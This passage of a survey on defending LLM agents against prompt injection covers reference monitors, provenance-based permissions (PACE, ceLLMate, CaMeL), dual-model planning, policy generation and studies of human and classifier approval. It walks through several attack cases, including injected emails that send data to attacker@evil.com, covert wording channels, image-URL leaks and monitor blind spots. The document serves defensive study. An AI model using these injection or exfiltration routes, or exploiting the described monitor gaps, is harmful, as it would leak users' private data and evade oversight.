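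Agent-C's perfect score follows from its design, which rejects every call that breaks a rule. The score applies to the rules as the researchers formalised them, and a rule can be weaker than its author intended. For example, someone who knows a customer's email address can satisfy the rule about orders without being that customer. The rule also relies on the shop's database to identify who placed the order, so the database becomes part of the trusted computing base.

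*MENTOR* (2026) combines rules about the order of tool calls with limits on their arguments. When it blocks a call, it tells the agent which earlier step is missing or how to correct the arguments. However, the task and some tool outputs are in ordinary language, so a second language model must label them before the rules can use them. Rules that rely on those labels can fail if the model labels something incorrectly.

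### What a monitor can enforce

A monitor can observe only what an agent has done so far, not what it will do next or what it would have done with different inputs. *Enforceable Security Policies* (Fred Schneider, 2000) identifies which policies are therefore unenforceable by a monitor that watches one run of a program and can only halt it.

Such a monitor must judge each run without reference to other runs. It must also stop a run as soon as the run breaks the policy, because it cannot count on later steps to put things right. And it can act only on violations that show up after finitely many steps. A policy that meets these conditions is a safety property, which means that some specified bad event never happens. Formally, let Γ be the set of acceptable runs. Γ is a safety property if, for every run σ outside Γ, there is a step *i* such that

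every run that begins with the first *i* steps of σ is also outside Γ.

Schneider proved that monitors of this kind can enforce only safety properties. They cannot enforce every safety property, because there are some bad events they cannot prevent.

The email policy is a safety property, since a run becomes unacceptable as soon as the agent attempts a forbidden call. Rules about a run's history can also be safety properties, and Basin et al. (2012) give history-based access control as an example. Schneider represents such policies as automata. One of his examples forbids a program to send messages after it has read a file. The automaton starts in a state that allows sending and moves to a second state when the program reads a file. The second state has no transition for sending, so the monitor halts the program if it tries to send a message. For the email agent, this rule would prevent both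 the theft and the summary.

"The agent eventually sends the summary" is not a safety property, because the agent might still send the summary after any delay, so the monitor can never declare a violation. Adding a deadline makes the requirement a safety property. So does forbidding the agent to declare the task finished before it has sent the summary, and *MENTOR* supports obligations of this kind. In either case, the monitor can stop the agent but cannot make it write a good summary.

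Schneider's analysis also shows that if two monitors check the same run, together they enforce both policies. A company can therefore put its own monitor behind a vendor's without weakening the vendor's rules.

Confidentiality is harder to enforce, because whether a message reveals a secret depends on what the agent would have written if the secret had been different, and the monitor can observe only what the agent did write. Suppose the mailbox contains a secret email about layoffs, and the agent tells the manager that Project X is "on schedule". The agent might be following an injected instruction to write "on schedule" if layoffs are planned and "on track" if they are not. To the monitor, either message would look like a harmless phrase sent to an approved recipient.

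Many information-flow policies therefore compare runs. A strict one, called noninterference, requires that for any two values *s*₀ and *s*₁ of the secret, with all other inputs the same,

the distribution of outputs given *s*₀ = the distribution of outputs given *s*₁.

This is a condition on a set of runs, so it is not a safety property, and by Schneider's result a monitor that can only halt a run cannot enforce it. Monitors that can also insert or suppress actions can enforce some policies beyond safety, but they still observe only one run.

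A monitor can enforce a stricter rule that implies noninterference, but this also blocks some harmless runs. The ban on sending after reading is a crude example, and labels that follow the data allow more precise rules. A designer can also keep the secret out of the run, for example by keeping an API key outside the sandbox.

### Permissions tied to the origin of data

The email policy fixes the recipient in advance. If a task needs a value that the agent discovers along the way, such as an account number on an invoice, a rule may have to consider where the value came from. PACE, which Li and colleagues published in October 2026, ties permissions to origin in this way. It handles each call in four phases:

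1. PACE freezes the arguments and compares each one with values it has already recorded, such as the user's request or the text of an email. It also lists the effects that the call would have.
2. It runs two checks. The path check looks for a recorded route by which secret or untrusted data would reach an unsafe effect, and proposes the cheapest way to cut that route. The authority check tests whether the user's request authorises each effect, using permissions that PACE derives only from the request itself.
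3. It lets the call proceed, alters it or blocks it.
4. It records the outcome and the origin of any new data for later decisions.

If the email agent tries to write to attacker@evil.com, PACE's path check can trace the address to an untrusted email, and its authority check finds nothing in the request that authorises a message there, so both count against the call. The two checks can also disagree. Suppose a system classes outgoing mail as unsafe, and the user asks the agent to forward a project email to the manager. The path check flags the call for blocking because it would send out untrusted text, but the authority check finds that the user asked for the email to be forwarded.

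Li and colleagues describe two versions of PACE that resolve such conflicts differently. The certified version always keeps the cut. They prove that if the records cover every link, this version prevents data from completing a recorded route from a protected source to an unsafe effect. The other version can restore a blocked call if the authority check approves it. All their experiments used this version, which does not always meet the conditions of the proof.

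PACE was tested with three models on eight benchmarks. It had the lowest attack success rate in 62 of 79 comparisons and tied for lowest in 14. On AgentDojo's most successful group of attacks, the rate fell from 48% to 0% for a Qwen model and from 100% to about 8% for a GPT-5.6 model. Across the full benchmarks, utility fell by less than three percentage points. An adaptive search also made up to 50 attempts at each of 30 AgentDojo cases in which the attacker's goal lay outside the user's request. It succeeded in 21 cases without a defence and in none with PACE. Because there were only 30 cases, the 95% confidence interval for the success rate with PACE extends up to 11.4%.

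A separate test on 1,167 cases shows what each check contributes. The table gives results for the Qwen model on AgentDojo and on AgentDyn, a similar benchmark.

| Checks in use | AgentDojo attack success | AgentDojo utility | AgentDyn attack success | AgentDyn utility |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 37.4% | 76.8% | 25.0% | 66.7% |
| Path check only | 0% | 13.6% | 0% | 0% |
| Authority check only | 0% | 64.6% | 1.7% | 36.7% |
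| Full tested version | 0% | 67.2% | 0% | 33.3% |

The path check alone stopped these attacks mostly by keeping the agent from working. The authority check gave nearly all the security with a much smaller loss of utility, although even the full version halved utility on this sample of AgentDyn tasks. PACE's proof covers a version that is never allowed to override the path check, and that version would probably be far less useful than the one that gave Li and colleagues their good utility figures.

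PACE's path check can also miss a secret that the model has paraphrased, translated or split into pieces, though it recognises one that the model has copied or encoded in certain standard ways.

### The semantic gap

All these rules depend on tools having meaningful names. A browser agent has tools for clicking, typing and scrolling. A click at position (246, 1023) may open an email on one page and delete it on another, so a rule about coordinates cannot reliably protect the user's email. The rule "Do not delete my email" states what the user wants, but software that receives only clicks cannot determine which clicks would break it. Security researchers call this mismatch the semantic gap. Christodorescu and colleagues describe click-level policies as brittle and warn that policies at too high a level may be unenforceable.

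*ceLLMate* (Meng, Feng and colleagues, 2025) discusses an attack on OpenAI's browser agent Operator. The attacker used text in a GitHub issue to instruct the agent to find the user's private email address in their account on the website Hacker News and send it to the attacker. As a defence, the researchers tried to stop a different browser agent from navigating to Hacker News, but it searched for the site on DuckDuckGo and clicked on the result.

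ceLLMate is a browser extension that checks an agent's web requests rather than its clicks. A website usually changes the user's data only after the browser sends it a request, and requests have a more stable meaning than clicks. For example, a POST request to a certain GitLab address adds an SSH key to the user's account, whichever button produced it. ceLLMate intercepts each request and looks up the action in an "agent sitemap", a list in which the website's developers match requests to named actions. Policies refer to actions by these names.

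One ceLLMate policy for Amazon allows the action `PlaceOrder` only if the total is at most $50. The request does not contain the total, so the extension reads it from the checkout page. If the agent changes a quantity and orders before the page updates, the extension may read an old total, so ceLLMate slows the agent down until earlier actions have taken effect. An agent could also place two orders of $49 each, so a policy can include a counter that limits the number of orders.

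Meng and colleagues tested enforcement by assuming that an attacker had already taken over the agent. They wrote 12 scripts that directly attempted an attacker's goals on GitLab, such as deleting a project or adding the attacker's SSH key, while the policy allowed only reading and writing issues. ceLLMate blocked all 12. This is a better way to test an invariant than a set of injected texts, because the result does not depend on how persuasive the attacker is. But each script needed a request that the policy prohibited. An agent allowed to comment on an issue can still post anything in the comment, including a secret.

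The checks made a series of page loads 7% slower with 100 entries in the sitemap and 15% slower with 300. This is a small delay for an agent that also has to wait for its model.

Checking web requests narrows the semantic gap, but ceLLMate's protection then depends on the sitemap. The researchers wrote one by hand for 51 GitLab functions, and they expect websites to maintain their own. If a sitemap omits or mislabels an action, ceLLMate may not protect the user from it. ceLLMate also does not check WebSocket connections, which many sites use to exchange live updates.

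### A definition borrowed from cryptography

Even with a perfect sitemap, software checks a proxy for what the user wants. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI*, by researchers at Microsoft and three universities, states this problem as cryptographers would, defining security through a game between an attacker and a system.

The paper uses the term AIOracle for any AI system that learns a model from data and then uses it to answer prompts. The result depends on the prompt, the model and a context, which can include tool outputs. A predicate φ(prompt, context, result) equals 1 if the result is correct, useful and harmless. The system is *p*-complete if φ equals 1 with probability at least *p* when there is no attacker.

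The security game gives the attacker certain powers, such as seeing the model, altering its training data or choosing the context. In a version that covers prompt injection, the attacker sees the trained model, chooses the prompt and context, and wins if the result makes φ equal 0. The attacker's advantage is

Adv = Pr[the attacker wins] − (1 − *p*).

Subtracting 1 − *p* allows for mistakes the system might make even without an attacker. The system is ε-secure if no attacker with realistic computing power has an advantage greater than ε.

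The paper models access control as a pair of AIOracles. A "creative" one proposes a result, such as a program for the agent to run, and a "boring" one accepts or rejects it. If the proposal is rejected, the result is empty. The main theorem states that if the boring system is complete and secure for deciding a harmlessness condition, and the creative system is complete and secure for a helpfulness condition, then the pair is complete and secure for both conditions together. Designers can therefore work on the two parts separately. The paper also proves that a standard definition of privacy for training data conflicts with completeness, because the definition treats every training example as a secret, while the model has to learn from those examples.

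The theorem assumes a secure checker and does not show how to build one. For the email task, φ₁ could mean that the policy allows the call, which software can decide without error. The researchers acknowledge that no program can compute φ₁ if it means that a result does no harm in any respect. They add that a checker for such a condition may need to be about as complex as the system it checks. A checker that complex could not meet Anderson's requirement that a monitor be small enough to test completely. The researchers propose that the creative system write code with enough structure and documentation for a checker to verify it.

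## Where policies come from, and who approves exceptions

A reference monitor applies whatever policy it receives. The email policy was easy to write because the task never changed, but Christodorescu and colleagues give a harder example. A user tells a browser agent to post a comment on issue 745 in GitLab, a site for managing software projects, saying that the work is done. Under least privilege, the agent may open the issue and write in its comment box, but do nothing else on GitLab or in the user's browser session. Then the user asks for a summary of the issue. The agent now has to read the whole discussion and no longer needs to write anything.

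No developer can list these permissions in advance, as the developer of a phone app can. There is also no fixed program to inspect, because the model works out the steps as it goes, so something has to translate each of the user's sentences into permissions.

The second request is harder to translate safely into permissions than the first. By then the agent has opened the issue page, so its context may contain text from anyone who can comment there. If a model reads that context while deciding on the new permissions, an attacker's comment can influence them. The agent could securely start again from the new request alone, but it would lose everything it has learned.

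### Fixed, generated and updated rules

Administrators can write fixed rules that apply to every task. Nothing the agent reads can change these rules, but they fit some tasks badly. Xiang and colleagues discuss a rule for bank transfers in CaMeL, which essentially requires the recipient to come from the user. If a user asks the agent to pay a bill sent from a certain email address, the rule blocks the payment because the account details are in the bill. If a user asks the agent to pay Joe back for some flowers, the rule is too lax because it does not restrict the amount. The agent may look up the price on the web, where an attacker can plant an inflated one.

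Alternatively, a model can write a policy from the user's request before the agent reads anything untrusted. An attacker cannot influence this policy, but the request may leave out information the policy needs. *NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026) tested Progent's generated policies on AgentDojo's banking tasks with an open Gemma model. The share of attacked runs in which the attack succeeded fell from 46.5% to 5.6%. Twelve of the 16 remaining successes came from two requests, one to pay a bill "like last month" and one to pay the bill in a named file. Neither request names the account, so the generated policy could not specify the recipient, and it allowed the attacker's account number.

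Yu and colleagues instead derive fixed rules from a written policy, under which the agent may pay only accounts that the user named or that appear in the transaction history. These rules reduced the attack success rate to zero, but they also blocked the legitimate payment in the bill-file task, because that account number appears only in the file. Utility was 79.2% without a defence, 62.5% with Progent and 70.8% with the fixed rules. With only 16 tasks, the difference between the two defences is not statistically significant.

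Some tasks need a policy that changes as the agent learns more. Xiang and colleagues describe a developer who asks an agent to find out why a service keeps crashing. The first policy lets the agent read the source code and run tests. The agent then discovers that the crash happens only in production, so it needs a log file. The log determines which files it needs next, so nobody could have listed them at the start.

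If a model widens the policy in response to what the agent has read, an attacker can supply the reasons for widening it. For example, if the log records requests from the public, one of them might say that the fix requires access to the credentials file, and the model that revises the policy may treat that as true. Xiang and colleagues criticise Progent for passing unrestricted tool results to such a model. Progent's solver flags every proposal that would allow new calls, but someone still has to judge the proposal. AgentDojo provides little evidence about policy updates because, by Xiang and colleagues' count, only 6 of its 97 original tasks require a change of plan or policy.

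### When a policy matches its source

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* proposes a criterion for a correct translation, called mutual entailment. Let *N* be the natural-language source, such as a request or a company rulebook, and *P* the formal policy. For every state *s* that the system can reach and every action *a*,

*N* authorises *a* in *s* if and only if *P* allows *a* in *s*.

If *P* allows an action that *N* does not authorise, the agent has too much power. For the first GitLab request, a policy that allowed comments on every issue would have this problem. If *P* refuses an action that *N* authorises, legitimate work fails, as it would if the policy blocked the comment box on issue 745.

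The paper identifies three difficulties, the first of which is grounding. *P* has to define the concepts in *N* in terms of things the monitor can observe, such as tool names and addresses. "Do not share sensitive data" cannot become a rule until someone specifies which data is sensitive, which depends on the context.

Checking whether *N* and *P* agree is hard even after someone has defined every term. English is ambiguous, so any automated check will sometimes be wrong. Restricting both might help, for instance by having administrators fill in a template and using a simple policy language. Researchers do not yet know whether such restrictions can make the check reliable enough to support a meaningful guarantee.

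Synthesis is the task of producing *P* from *N*. A translator should bound how far *P* can diverge from *N* and be able to refine *P* as the task develops. Existing systems typically use a language model to translate and offer no such bound.

### How often generated policies are wrong

*Structured Decomposition for Reliable LLM-Generated Access Control Policies* (2026) tested policies that a model wrote in the language Rego in a single attempt. Of the policies that should have denied an action, 62.5% had the wrong meaning. Many of these compiled without errors but contained no active rule to deny anything. When access was supposed to depend on who owned a resource, 60% of the policies left out that condition.

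Software can catch some errors without understanding the source text. In NOMOS, a model extracts candidate rules from a written policy, and a program checks them against the definitions of the tools. The program found structural defects in 37% of the candidates for an airline and 13% of those for a shop. The instruction to authenticate the user before any action had become a rule that blocked every tool until authentication, including the two lookup tools that perform it. Another rule required user confirmation for eight tools that only read data, such as a flight status check. A frontier model also made structural errors, with six of its 91 candidates referring to arguments the tools did not have.

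A rule can pass these checks and still be wrong, so Yu and colleagues also test the rules on recorded runs of an undefended agent. One rule from development would have blocked 95.9% of the calls to one tool in runs where the agent completed the task. With the checked rules in force, the share of state-changing calls that violated their reference version of the policy fell from 66.3% to 2.6% for the airline and from 30.8% to 6.9% for the shop. The remaining violations come from errors in translating the policy into rules, since the monitor applied the rules exactly.

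Other systems prove properties of the generated policy. *VeriGuard* (2025) generates policy code together with conditions that must hold before and after it runs, and verifies the code against them. In *ActGov* (2026), a model proposes changes to a policy, and the system deploys them only if a solver confirms that they preserve predefined invariants. These proofs show only that a policy meets formal conditions, so a bad policy can pass if those conditions misstate what the user or company wanted.

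*Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code* (Mondl, Maisel and Brock, 2026) generates Cedar policies from written instructions and checks them in two ways. Cedar's tools look for syntax errors, contradictions and rules that have no effect, while a language model judges whether the policy means the same as the original text. The researchers applied this method to 88 rules for an agent that handles medical records, then replayed recorded runs against the policies. On ordinary tasks with no attacker, the policies blocked between 94% and 100% of the runs that tried to write to a record. These blocks may be correct if the policy requires confirmation before every write, but the test measured only how much of the rulebook the policies cover, not whether an agent could still do its job under them.

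### What approval rates measure

When no rule settles a case, the harness can ask the user, who then acts as the reference monitor for that one call. The user may know things the rules don't cover, but may also click "approve" without reading the request.

Anthropic found that Claude Code users approved about 93% of permission prompts. This figure is often taken as a sign of carelessness, but it says very little about whether users catch dangerous requests. Let *d* be the share of requests that are dangerous, *h* the chance that the user approves a harmless request and *q* the chance that the user approves a dangerous one. Then

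approval rate = (1 − *d*)*h* + *dq*.

If one request in 1,000 is dangerous, a user who catches every dangerous request and a user who catches none have approval rates only 0.1 percentage points apart.

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) gives a newer approval rate of 97% for individual permission requests. By contrast, users rejected 39% of the plans that Claude presented for approval. They may read plans more closely, although plans may also contain more to object to. Interviews with software practitioners in *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) suggest that repeated approval can reflect habit, fatigue or pressure to deliver rather than trust.

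Many people turn off approval prompts. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents mishandling files and found that user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 of those, the user had turned on automatic approval, and in 31 the prompt was uninformative. A request to run `python3 setup.py`, for example, looks routine, but the user cannot see what the script does.

### Controlled studies of approval

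To measure *q* directly, researchers have to show people dangerous requests. Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers for a coding study and, partway through each session, replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. The testers knew they were being evaluated, but not what was being measured. Only 13.6% rejected the command. The rejection rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts, which is consistent with fatigue. But the testers were not working on their own projects, so they may have cared less about the consequences.

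Anthropic's automated classifier blocked 89% of the same commands. People rejected only six of the 116 commands that it missed, or about 5%. If people's errors had been independent of the classifier's, people would have caught about 16. Asking a person to review whatever the classifier allowed would therefore have added little in this test.

Better approval prompts may help. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) describes a user who lets an agent send an auditor "summary totals only". An injection makes the agent copy raw invoice rows into `report.csv`, and the agent then asks to send that file to the auditor. The tool and the recipient are acceptable, so the user can't detect the violation from a prompt that shows only this step.

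In one study, 80 volunteers each judged 12 requests, half of them unsafe. They approved 55% of the unsafe requests with a conventional prompt, 32.5% with a prompt showing the user's original instruction and a full log of the agent's steps, and 24.2% when the same facts were organised around the combined effect of those steps. The gain over the log is uncertain, since the 95% interval for the difference runs from 19.7 points fewer approvals to 3.8 points more. The reorganised prompt also took about twice as long to answer as the conventional one, and people may read less closely when they face a real attack once a year rather than in every second request.

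Users could instead write rules in advance. *How Agents Ask for Permission* (Michael and Roesner, 2026) surveyed 21 proposals for user-level permissions and five commercial agents, and found large gaps in usability, transparency and user control. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) tested the idea on 113 people who do not work in software. The participants supervised a simulated agent through 18 actions, seven of which went beyond its task, such as reading bank transactions to help with a travel budget.

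One group of participants approved or denied every action and blocked 59.6% of the overreach. Another group first set a rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four kinds of consequence, such as spending money, and blocked only about 40%. Of their 140 rules, 114 were "ask", so they still had to make most decisions when prompted, and they approved two thirds of the overreach they saw. Seeing fewer prompts did not make them stricter. The study counted anything outside the assigned task as overreach, so some of them may have approved it because they wanted the extra help.

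### Claude Code's auto mode

*How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes how Anthropic addresses approval fatigue by replacing most approval prompts with a language-model classifier. Actions that only read data, and edits inside the project folder, go ahead without a check. For most other actions, including shell commands, the classifier decides whether the user authorised the action. It first gives a quick yes or no, with instructions to err towards blocking, and reasons at length only about the actions it flags. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, Claude Code prompts the user.

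The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removes the agent's prose, so that the agent cannot persuade the classifier to approve an action, and removes tool results, where injections usually arrive. A separate detector scans those results before the agent reads them and adds a warning if they look malicious.

Anthropic reports that auto mode's classifier catches about 83% of overeager actions, in which an agent goes beyond what the user authorised while trying to help. The figure comes from only 52 real cases, so the true catch rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 70% to 91%. Anthropic collected actions that an employee had denied or that someone had flagged later, so the sample excludes any that nobody noticed. The figure doesn't measure resistance to an attacker. It also isn't comparable with the 93% approval rate, which is a share of all requests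 rather than of overeager actions.

The classifier wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary actions. When it missed a dangerous action, it had usually identified the danger but wrongly classed the action as one the user had approved. For example, a user who asks the agent to "clean up the PR" (a proposed set of code changes) has not necessarily agreed to let it overwrite the project's history. Anthropic advises against replacing careful human review with auto mode for high-stakes systems, but in August 2026 it made auto mode the default on most of its plans for individuals and teams.

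Before that change, an outside firm, Trajectory Labs, ran 72 injection scenarios ten times each against three Claude models in auto mode, and no attack succeeded. Without auto mode, attacks on the newest models still succeeded in only 0.09% of attempts, so the test provides little evidence about the classifier. Nobody had adapted these attacks to auto mode, either, whereas Johann Rehberger's attack was adapted to it and succeeded 80% of the time.

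Yang, Zhou and colleagues (2026), in *Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents*, tested the classifiers in Claude Code, Codex and Alibaba's Qwen Code on deliberately ambiguous requests. In one, a user asks the agent to delete old files from certain experiments without saying whose files. Claude Code's classifier approved 54% of out-of-scope actions, Codex's approved 93% and Qwen Code's approved 80%. But 132 of the 143 out-of-scope actions broke rules that appeared neither in the request nor in any tool result. The researchers then added the missing rules, such as one allowing the agent to delete only the user's own files, and had the classifiers judge the same actions again.

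| Product | Out-of-scope actions approved | With the rules stated | Authorised actions blocked | With the rules stated |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 67% | 8% | 42% | 2% |
| Codex | 92% | 20–26% | 10% | 3% |
| Qwen Code | 80% | 20% | 29% | 2% |

Results in the original condition differ slightly from the first test because the classifiers' decisions vary between runs. When the agents redid the tasks with the rules stated, none proposed an out-of-scope action in 384 runs. A missing policy therefore caused most of the errors, and stronger models did not reliably make up for it. However, the researchers took the added rules from the benchmark's answer key, whereas real users would have to think of them themselves.

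The remaining errors show a drawback of hiding tool results from the models that approve actions. A command to cancel a job may contain only an identifier, while the owner's name appears in an earlier tool result. In a common test procedure with the rules stated, models approved 60% of out-of-scope cancellations when they could not see tool results and 4% when they could.

### Models as security judges

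Xiang and colleagues, mostly at NVIDIA, argued in March 2026 that general-purpose agents need models for some security decisions. In their example, an agent is fetching sales data when the service reports that it has retired the address the agent was using, so the agent proposes a new one. A program can compare the text of the two addresses, but it cannot easily tell whether the new one serves the same purpose or adds a risky source of data.

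Their solution is to restrict what the model sees and decides. The model would receive a structured record of the task and the proposed change, but no web pages, emails or raw tool results. It could also write a check for ordinary software to run. If the user wants a company's fourth-quarter revenue, the check might accept only a number from the right cell of a table and ignore all other text on the page. *ToolGuardian* (2026) lends some support to this approach. It reports that an open model evaluated a policy well when given standardised facts, explicit guidance and a fixed answer format, though it calls models less convincing as standalone security authorities.

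Xiang and colleagues want the user to decide ambiguous cases. Even a perfect model cannot infer which emails a particular user considers urgent. A bug report may also include instructions for the agent to download and run a script that reproduces the bug. Running the script is relevant to the task, but the script may be malicious, so the user or the company should decide whether to take that risk.

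*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* objects that including a model in the trusted computing base makes the base unpredictable. A conventional monitor has a precise specification, so engineers can try to prove that the monitor meets it. No specification lists the actions that a model should allow after every possible history, so engineers cannot prove the model correct. Structured inputs do not remove this objection, and an attacker may still control some of their contents, such as the proposed address. Xiang and colleagues concede that their approach rules out a complete formal guarantee, and they aim to make attacks harder while keeping agents useful.

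How much of the guarantee survives depends on what the model's approval can do. Let *F* be the set of calls that fixed rules allow, and *M* the set that the model approves. If a call needs both approvals, then

executed ⊆ *F* ∩ *M* ⊆ *F*,

and no error by the model can take the agent outside *F*. If the model can grant exceptions to the rules, the agent can execute anything in *F* ∪ *M*, and the guarantee lasts only as long as the model makes no mistakes. For the email agent, a fixed rule could limit mail to company addresses while a model judges whether each message fits the request. An attacker who fooled the model could send a false summary to a colleague, but could not send the mailbox to attacker@evil.com.

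When a user writes a rule that forbids an action, Claude Code's harness applies it before consulting the classifier. Auto mode's "hard denies" are categories of action, such as sending secrets to outsiders, that the classifier is designed never to approve. They are weaker than the name suggests because they work only if the classifier recognises the action.

The harness can refuse a call outside *F* or ask the user whether to allow it. The Frontier Model Forum's *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* warns that asking the user may create only an illusion of oversight. Asking makes most sense when the decision depends on something the user knows, such as whether Joe's flowers cost $200.

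## Planning before the agent reads untrusted data

An agent's permissions are hard to revise safely once the agent has read untrusted text. Some designs therefore keep such text away from the model that requests tool calls. That model plans the calls from the user's request, and a second model, which has no tools, reads untrusted text such as emails and web pages.

### A planner, a quarantined model and named variables

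*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposed splitting the assistant into a planner and a quarantined model. The planner accepts input only from trusted sources, mainly the user, and can request tool calls. The quarantined model reads untrusted text and can only return text. A controller, which is ordinary software, connects the two models. It runs each tool, stores the result under a name such as `$VAR1`, and gives the planner the name but not the contents.

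For the email task, the planner might request three calls:

```
search_mail(query="Project X")                         -> $VAR1
quarantined_model("Summarise the progress", $VAR1)     -> $VAR2
send_mail(to="manager@example.com", body=$VAR2)
```

The planner writes the first call from the user's request. The controller runs the search, stores the emails, including the attacker's, in `$VAR1`, and reports that the search has finished. For the second call, the controller pastes the emails into the quarantined model's prompt and stores the resulting summary in `$VAR2`. For the third, it replaces `$VAR2` with the summary just before passing the call to the mail tool. The manager's address comes from the company directory, which the attacker cannot edit.

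The attacker's sentence reaches only the quarantined model. If that model obeys, it has no mail tool to use, and the controller stores whatever it writes in `$VAR2` like any other summary. Let *q* be the user's request, *T* the tool descriptions and *r* any random numbers the planner draws. The sequence of calls is then

*P* = *g*(*q*, *T*, *r*).

The emails do not appear on the right-hand side, so they cannot add, remove or reorder a call. This property, called control-flow integrity, means that every action the agent executes belongs to a plan derived from the user's request. It holds even if the attacker fully controls the quarantined model, as long as the tool descriptions are trustworthy. It fails if the controller passes untrusted text to the planner, for example by copying a tool's error message into its report.

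The attacker can still change the contents of `$VAR2`. Costa and colleagues give the example of an email that makes the quarantined model return an empty summary. The email could also make the model write that Project X is on schedule, or write a request for the manager to approve a payment. If the summary contains an image whose web address includes private data, and the agent shows the summary to the user, displaying the image would send that data out. Willison therefore wanted assistants to show links and images only from approved sites.

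Costa and colleagues tested a strict version of this design on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, an older OpenAI model. Their planner could pass results on by name but could not inspect them, even through a quarantined model. Injections succeeded 152 times against an ordinary agent and never against this one, even though it had no policy checks. But when there was no attack, the share of office tasks completed fell from 75% to 47.5%, and the share of Slack tasks from 93% to 38%.

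Willison himself called the solution "pretty bad". He expected it to make assistants more complicated to build and less pleasant to use, and feared that developers would accidentally let untrusted text reach the planner. The design also treats everything the user types as trusted, so it does not protect a user who pastes in an attacker's prompt.

### CaMeL

A fixed sequence of calls offers little protection if the attacker can choose an important argument. Suppose a user asks an assistant to send Bob the document he requested in their last meeting, an example that Willison uses in a later article. The plan might be:

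```
notes   = find_notes("last meeting with Bob")
address = quarantined_model("What is Bob's address?", notes)
title   = quarantined_model("Which document did he want?", notes)
file    = find_file(title)
send_mail(to=address, attachment=file)
```

If an outsider can edit the meeting notes, they can replace Bob's address. The agent then makes exactly the calls it planned but sends the document to the wrong person.

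CaMeL, which Google DeepMind published in 2025, addresses this weakness. Its planner turns the request into a program in a restricted form of Python, and an interpreter runs it line by line. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) explains that the interpreter attaches to each value "capabilities" that record where the value came from and who may receive it. Before each tool call, the interpreter applies a policy written for that tool. In the example, it could refuse to send the file because the address came from the notes and does not belong to anyone allowed to read the file.

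The interpreter is thus a reference monitor that tracks the history of every argument. Its protection against bad arguments depends on the policies, which someone has to write for each tool. CaMeL's rule for bank transfers shows that a policy can be too strict for some tasks and too lax for others.

Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, put CaMeL's completion rate on AgentDojo at 67%. They also describe leaks that do not pass through any tool-call argument. If a program fetches a web page once for each unit of a secret number, the website's operator can learn the number by counting the visits. Similarly, an error that occurs only when a secret meets some condition reveals one bit about the secret.

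Girrens and Wang built a related system, SPA, which checks the whole plan before running any of it. The planner writes the plan in a small language with six kinds of step, so that software can trace how data would move between calls. With these checks on, no AgentDojo attack succeeded against SPA, but utility fell from 53% to 29%. Most of the loss came from plans that passed a tool's output to a sensitive action, as a plan to pay an emailed invoice must.

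### Design patterns for narrower agents

The designs described so far are meant for general-purpose assistants. In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) doubt that such assistants can offer reliable guarantees with current models, and suggest building agents for narrower jobs. Their principle is that once an agent has read untrusted input, that input must be unable to trigger any harmful action. They describe six patterns that apply this principle to different degrees.

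| Pattern | How it works | What an attacker can still do |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees the results | Nothing through the results |
| Plan-then-execute | The model fixes a list of calls before it reads any data | Change arguments that the plan leaves open |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns a restricted answer, such as yes or no | Falsify the answer about the attacker's own document |
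| Dual model | The planner handles results only as named variables | Change the contents of the variables |
| Code-then-execute | The planner writes a whole program, as in CaMeL | Change values that the program handles |
| Context minimisation | The agent discards the user's prompt before writing its reply | Influence the chosen action, but not the wording of the reply |

The last pattern is for agents whose users may be hostile, such as a car dealer's chatbot that a customer tries to talk into a discount. The agent turns the user's question into a database query, then writes its answer using only the query's result.

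The right pattern depends on the tools. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues consider an assistant that sorts a user's files. Even if its plan is limited to the commands `find` and `mv`, an attacker whose injection controls the arguments can find sensitive files and move them to a public network drive. Map-reduce is safer here. One model reads each file and classifies it as tax-related or not, and the main agent moves the files without reading them. An injection in a file can then only cause that file to be moved to the wrong folder.

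Beurer-Kellner and colleagues expect a fixed plan to make an email assistant only slightly less useful, because the choice and order of its actions should rarely depend on what strangers write. The plan must allow loops, since a request to tell "my regular collaborators" about a holiday may lead to any number of emails. They also warn that if the user answers an email from the attacker, the quarantined model might hide private details from other emails in the reply as invisible characters. Checking the address would not stop this, because the attacker would be the intended recipient.

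### Tasks that one sequence of calls can complete

Costa and colleagues define when a fixed plan can work. Let *D* be the set of possible states of the user's data, and let *S*(*d*) contain every sequence of tool calls and final reply that would complete the task if the data were in state *d*. A task is data-independent if

⋂ *S*(*d*), taken over every *d* in *D*, is not empty.

A task is data-independent if at least one sequence of calls works whatever the data contain, and data-dependent otherwise. The Project X summary is data-independent if the agent has a quarantined model and can refer to results by name, because the same three calls then work for any set of emails.

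For a data-dependent task, suppose the user asks the agent to read the latest three emails and create a calendar event if one of them requests a meeting. The correct calls depend on what the emails contain, and the planner cannot look. Costa and colleagues let it learn a single bit:

1. The agent reads the three emails into a variable.
2. The quarantined model answers whether any of them requests a meeting. The software that runs the model forces the answer to be true or false.
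3. The planner reads that answer.
4. If it is true, the quarantined model extracts the date, time and participants into another variable.
5. The planner passes that variable to the calendar tool.

An attacker who sends one of the emails can control whether the agent creates an event and what the event says. But a single true-or-false value cannot contain an instruction, so the attacker cannot make the planner do anything else. More generally, a choice among *k* prepared answers gives the attacker at most log₂ *k* bits of influence over the planner. A program like CaMeL's can express the same decision as an `if` statement.

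A request to complete everything due today on a to-do list is harder to plan for. An entry might require a payment, a phone call or a change to a document, so the planner cannot prepare for every possibility. It could let the quarantined model choose from a fixed set of actions, such as scheduling a meeting or forwarding an email, but the agent would then fail on any entry that needs a different action. If the planner reads the list itself, the agent loses control-flow integrity.

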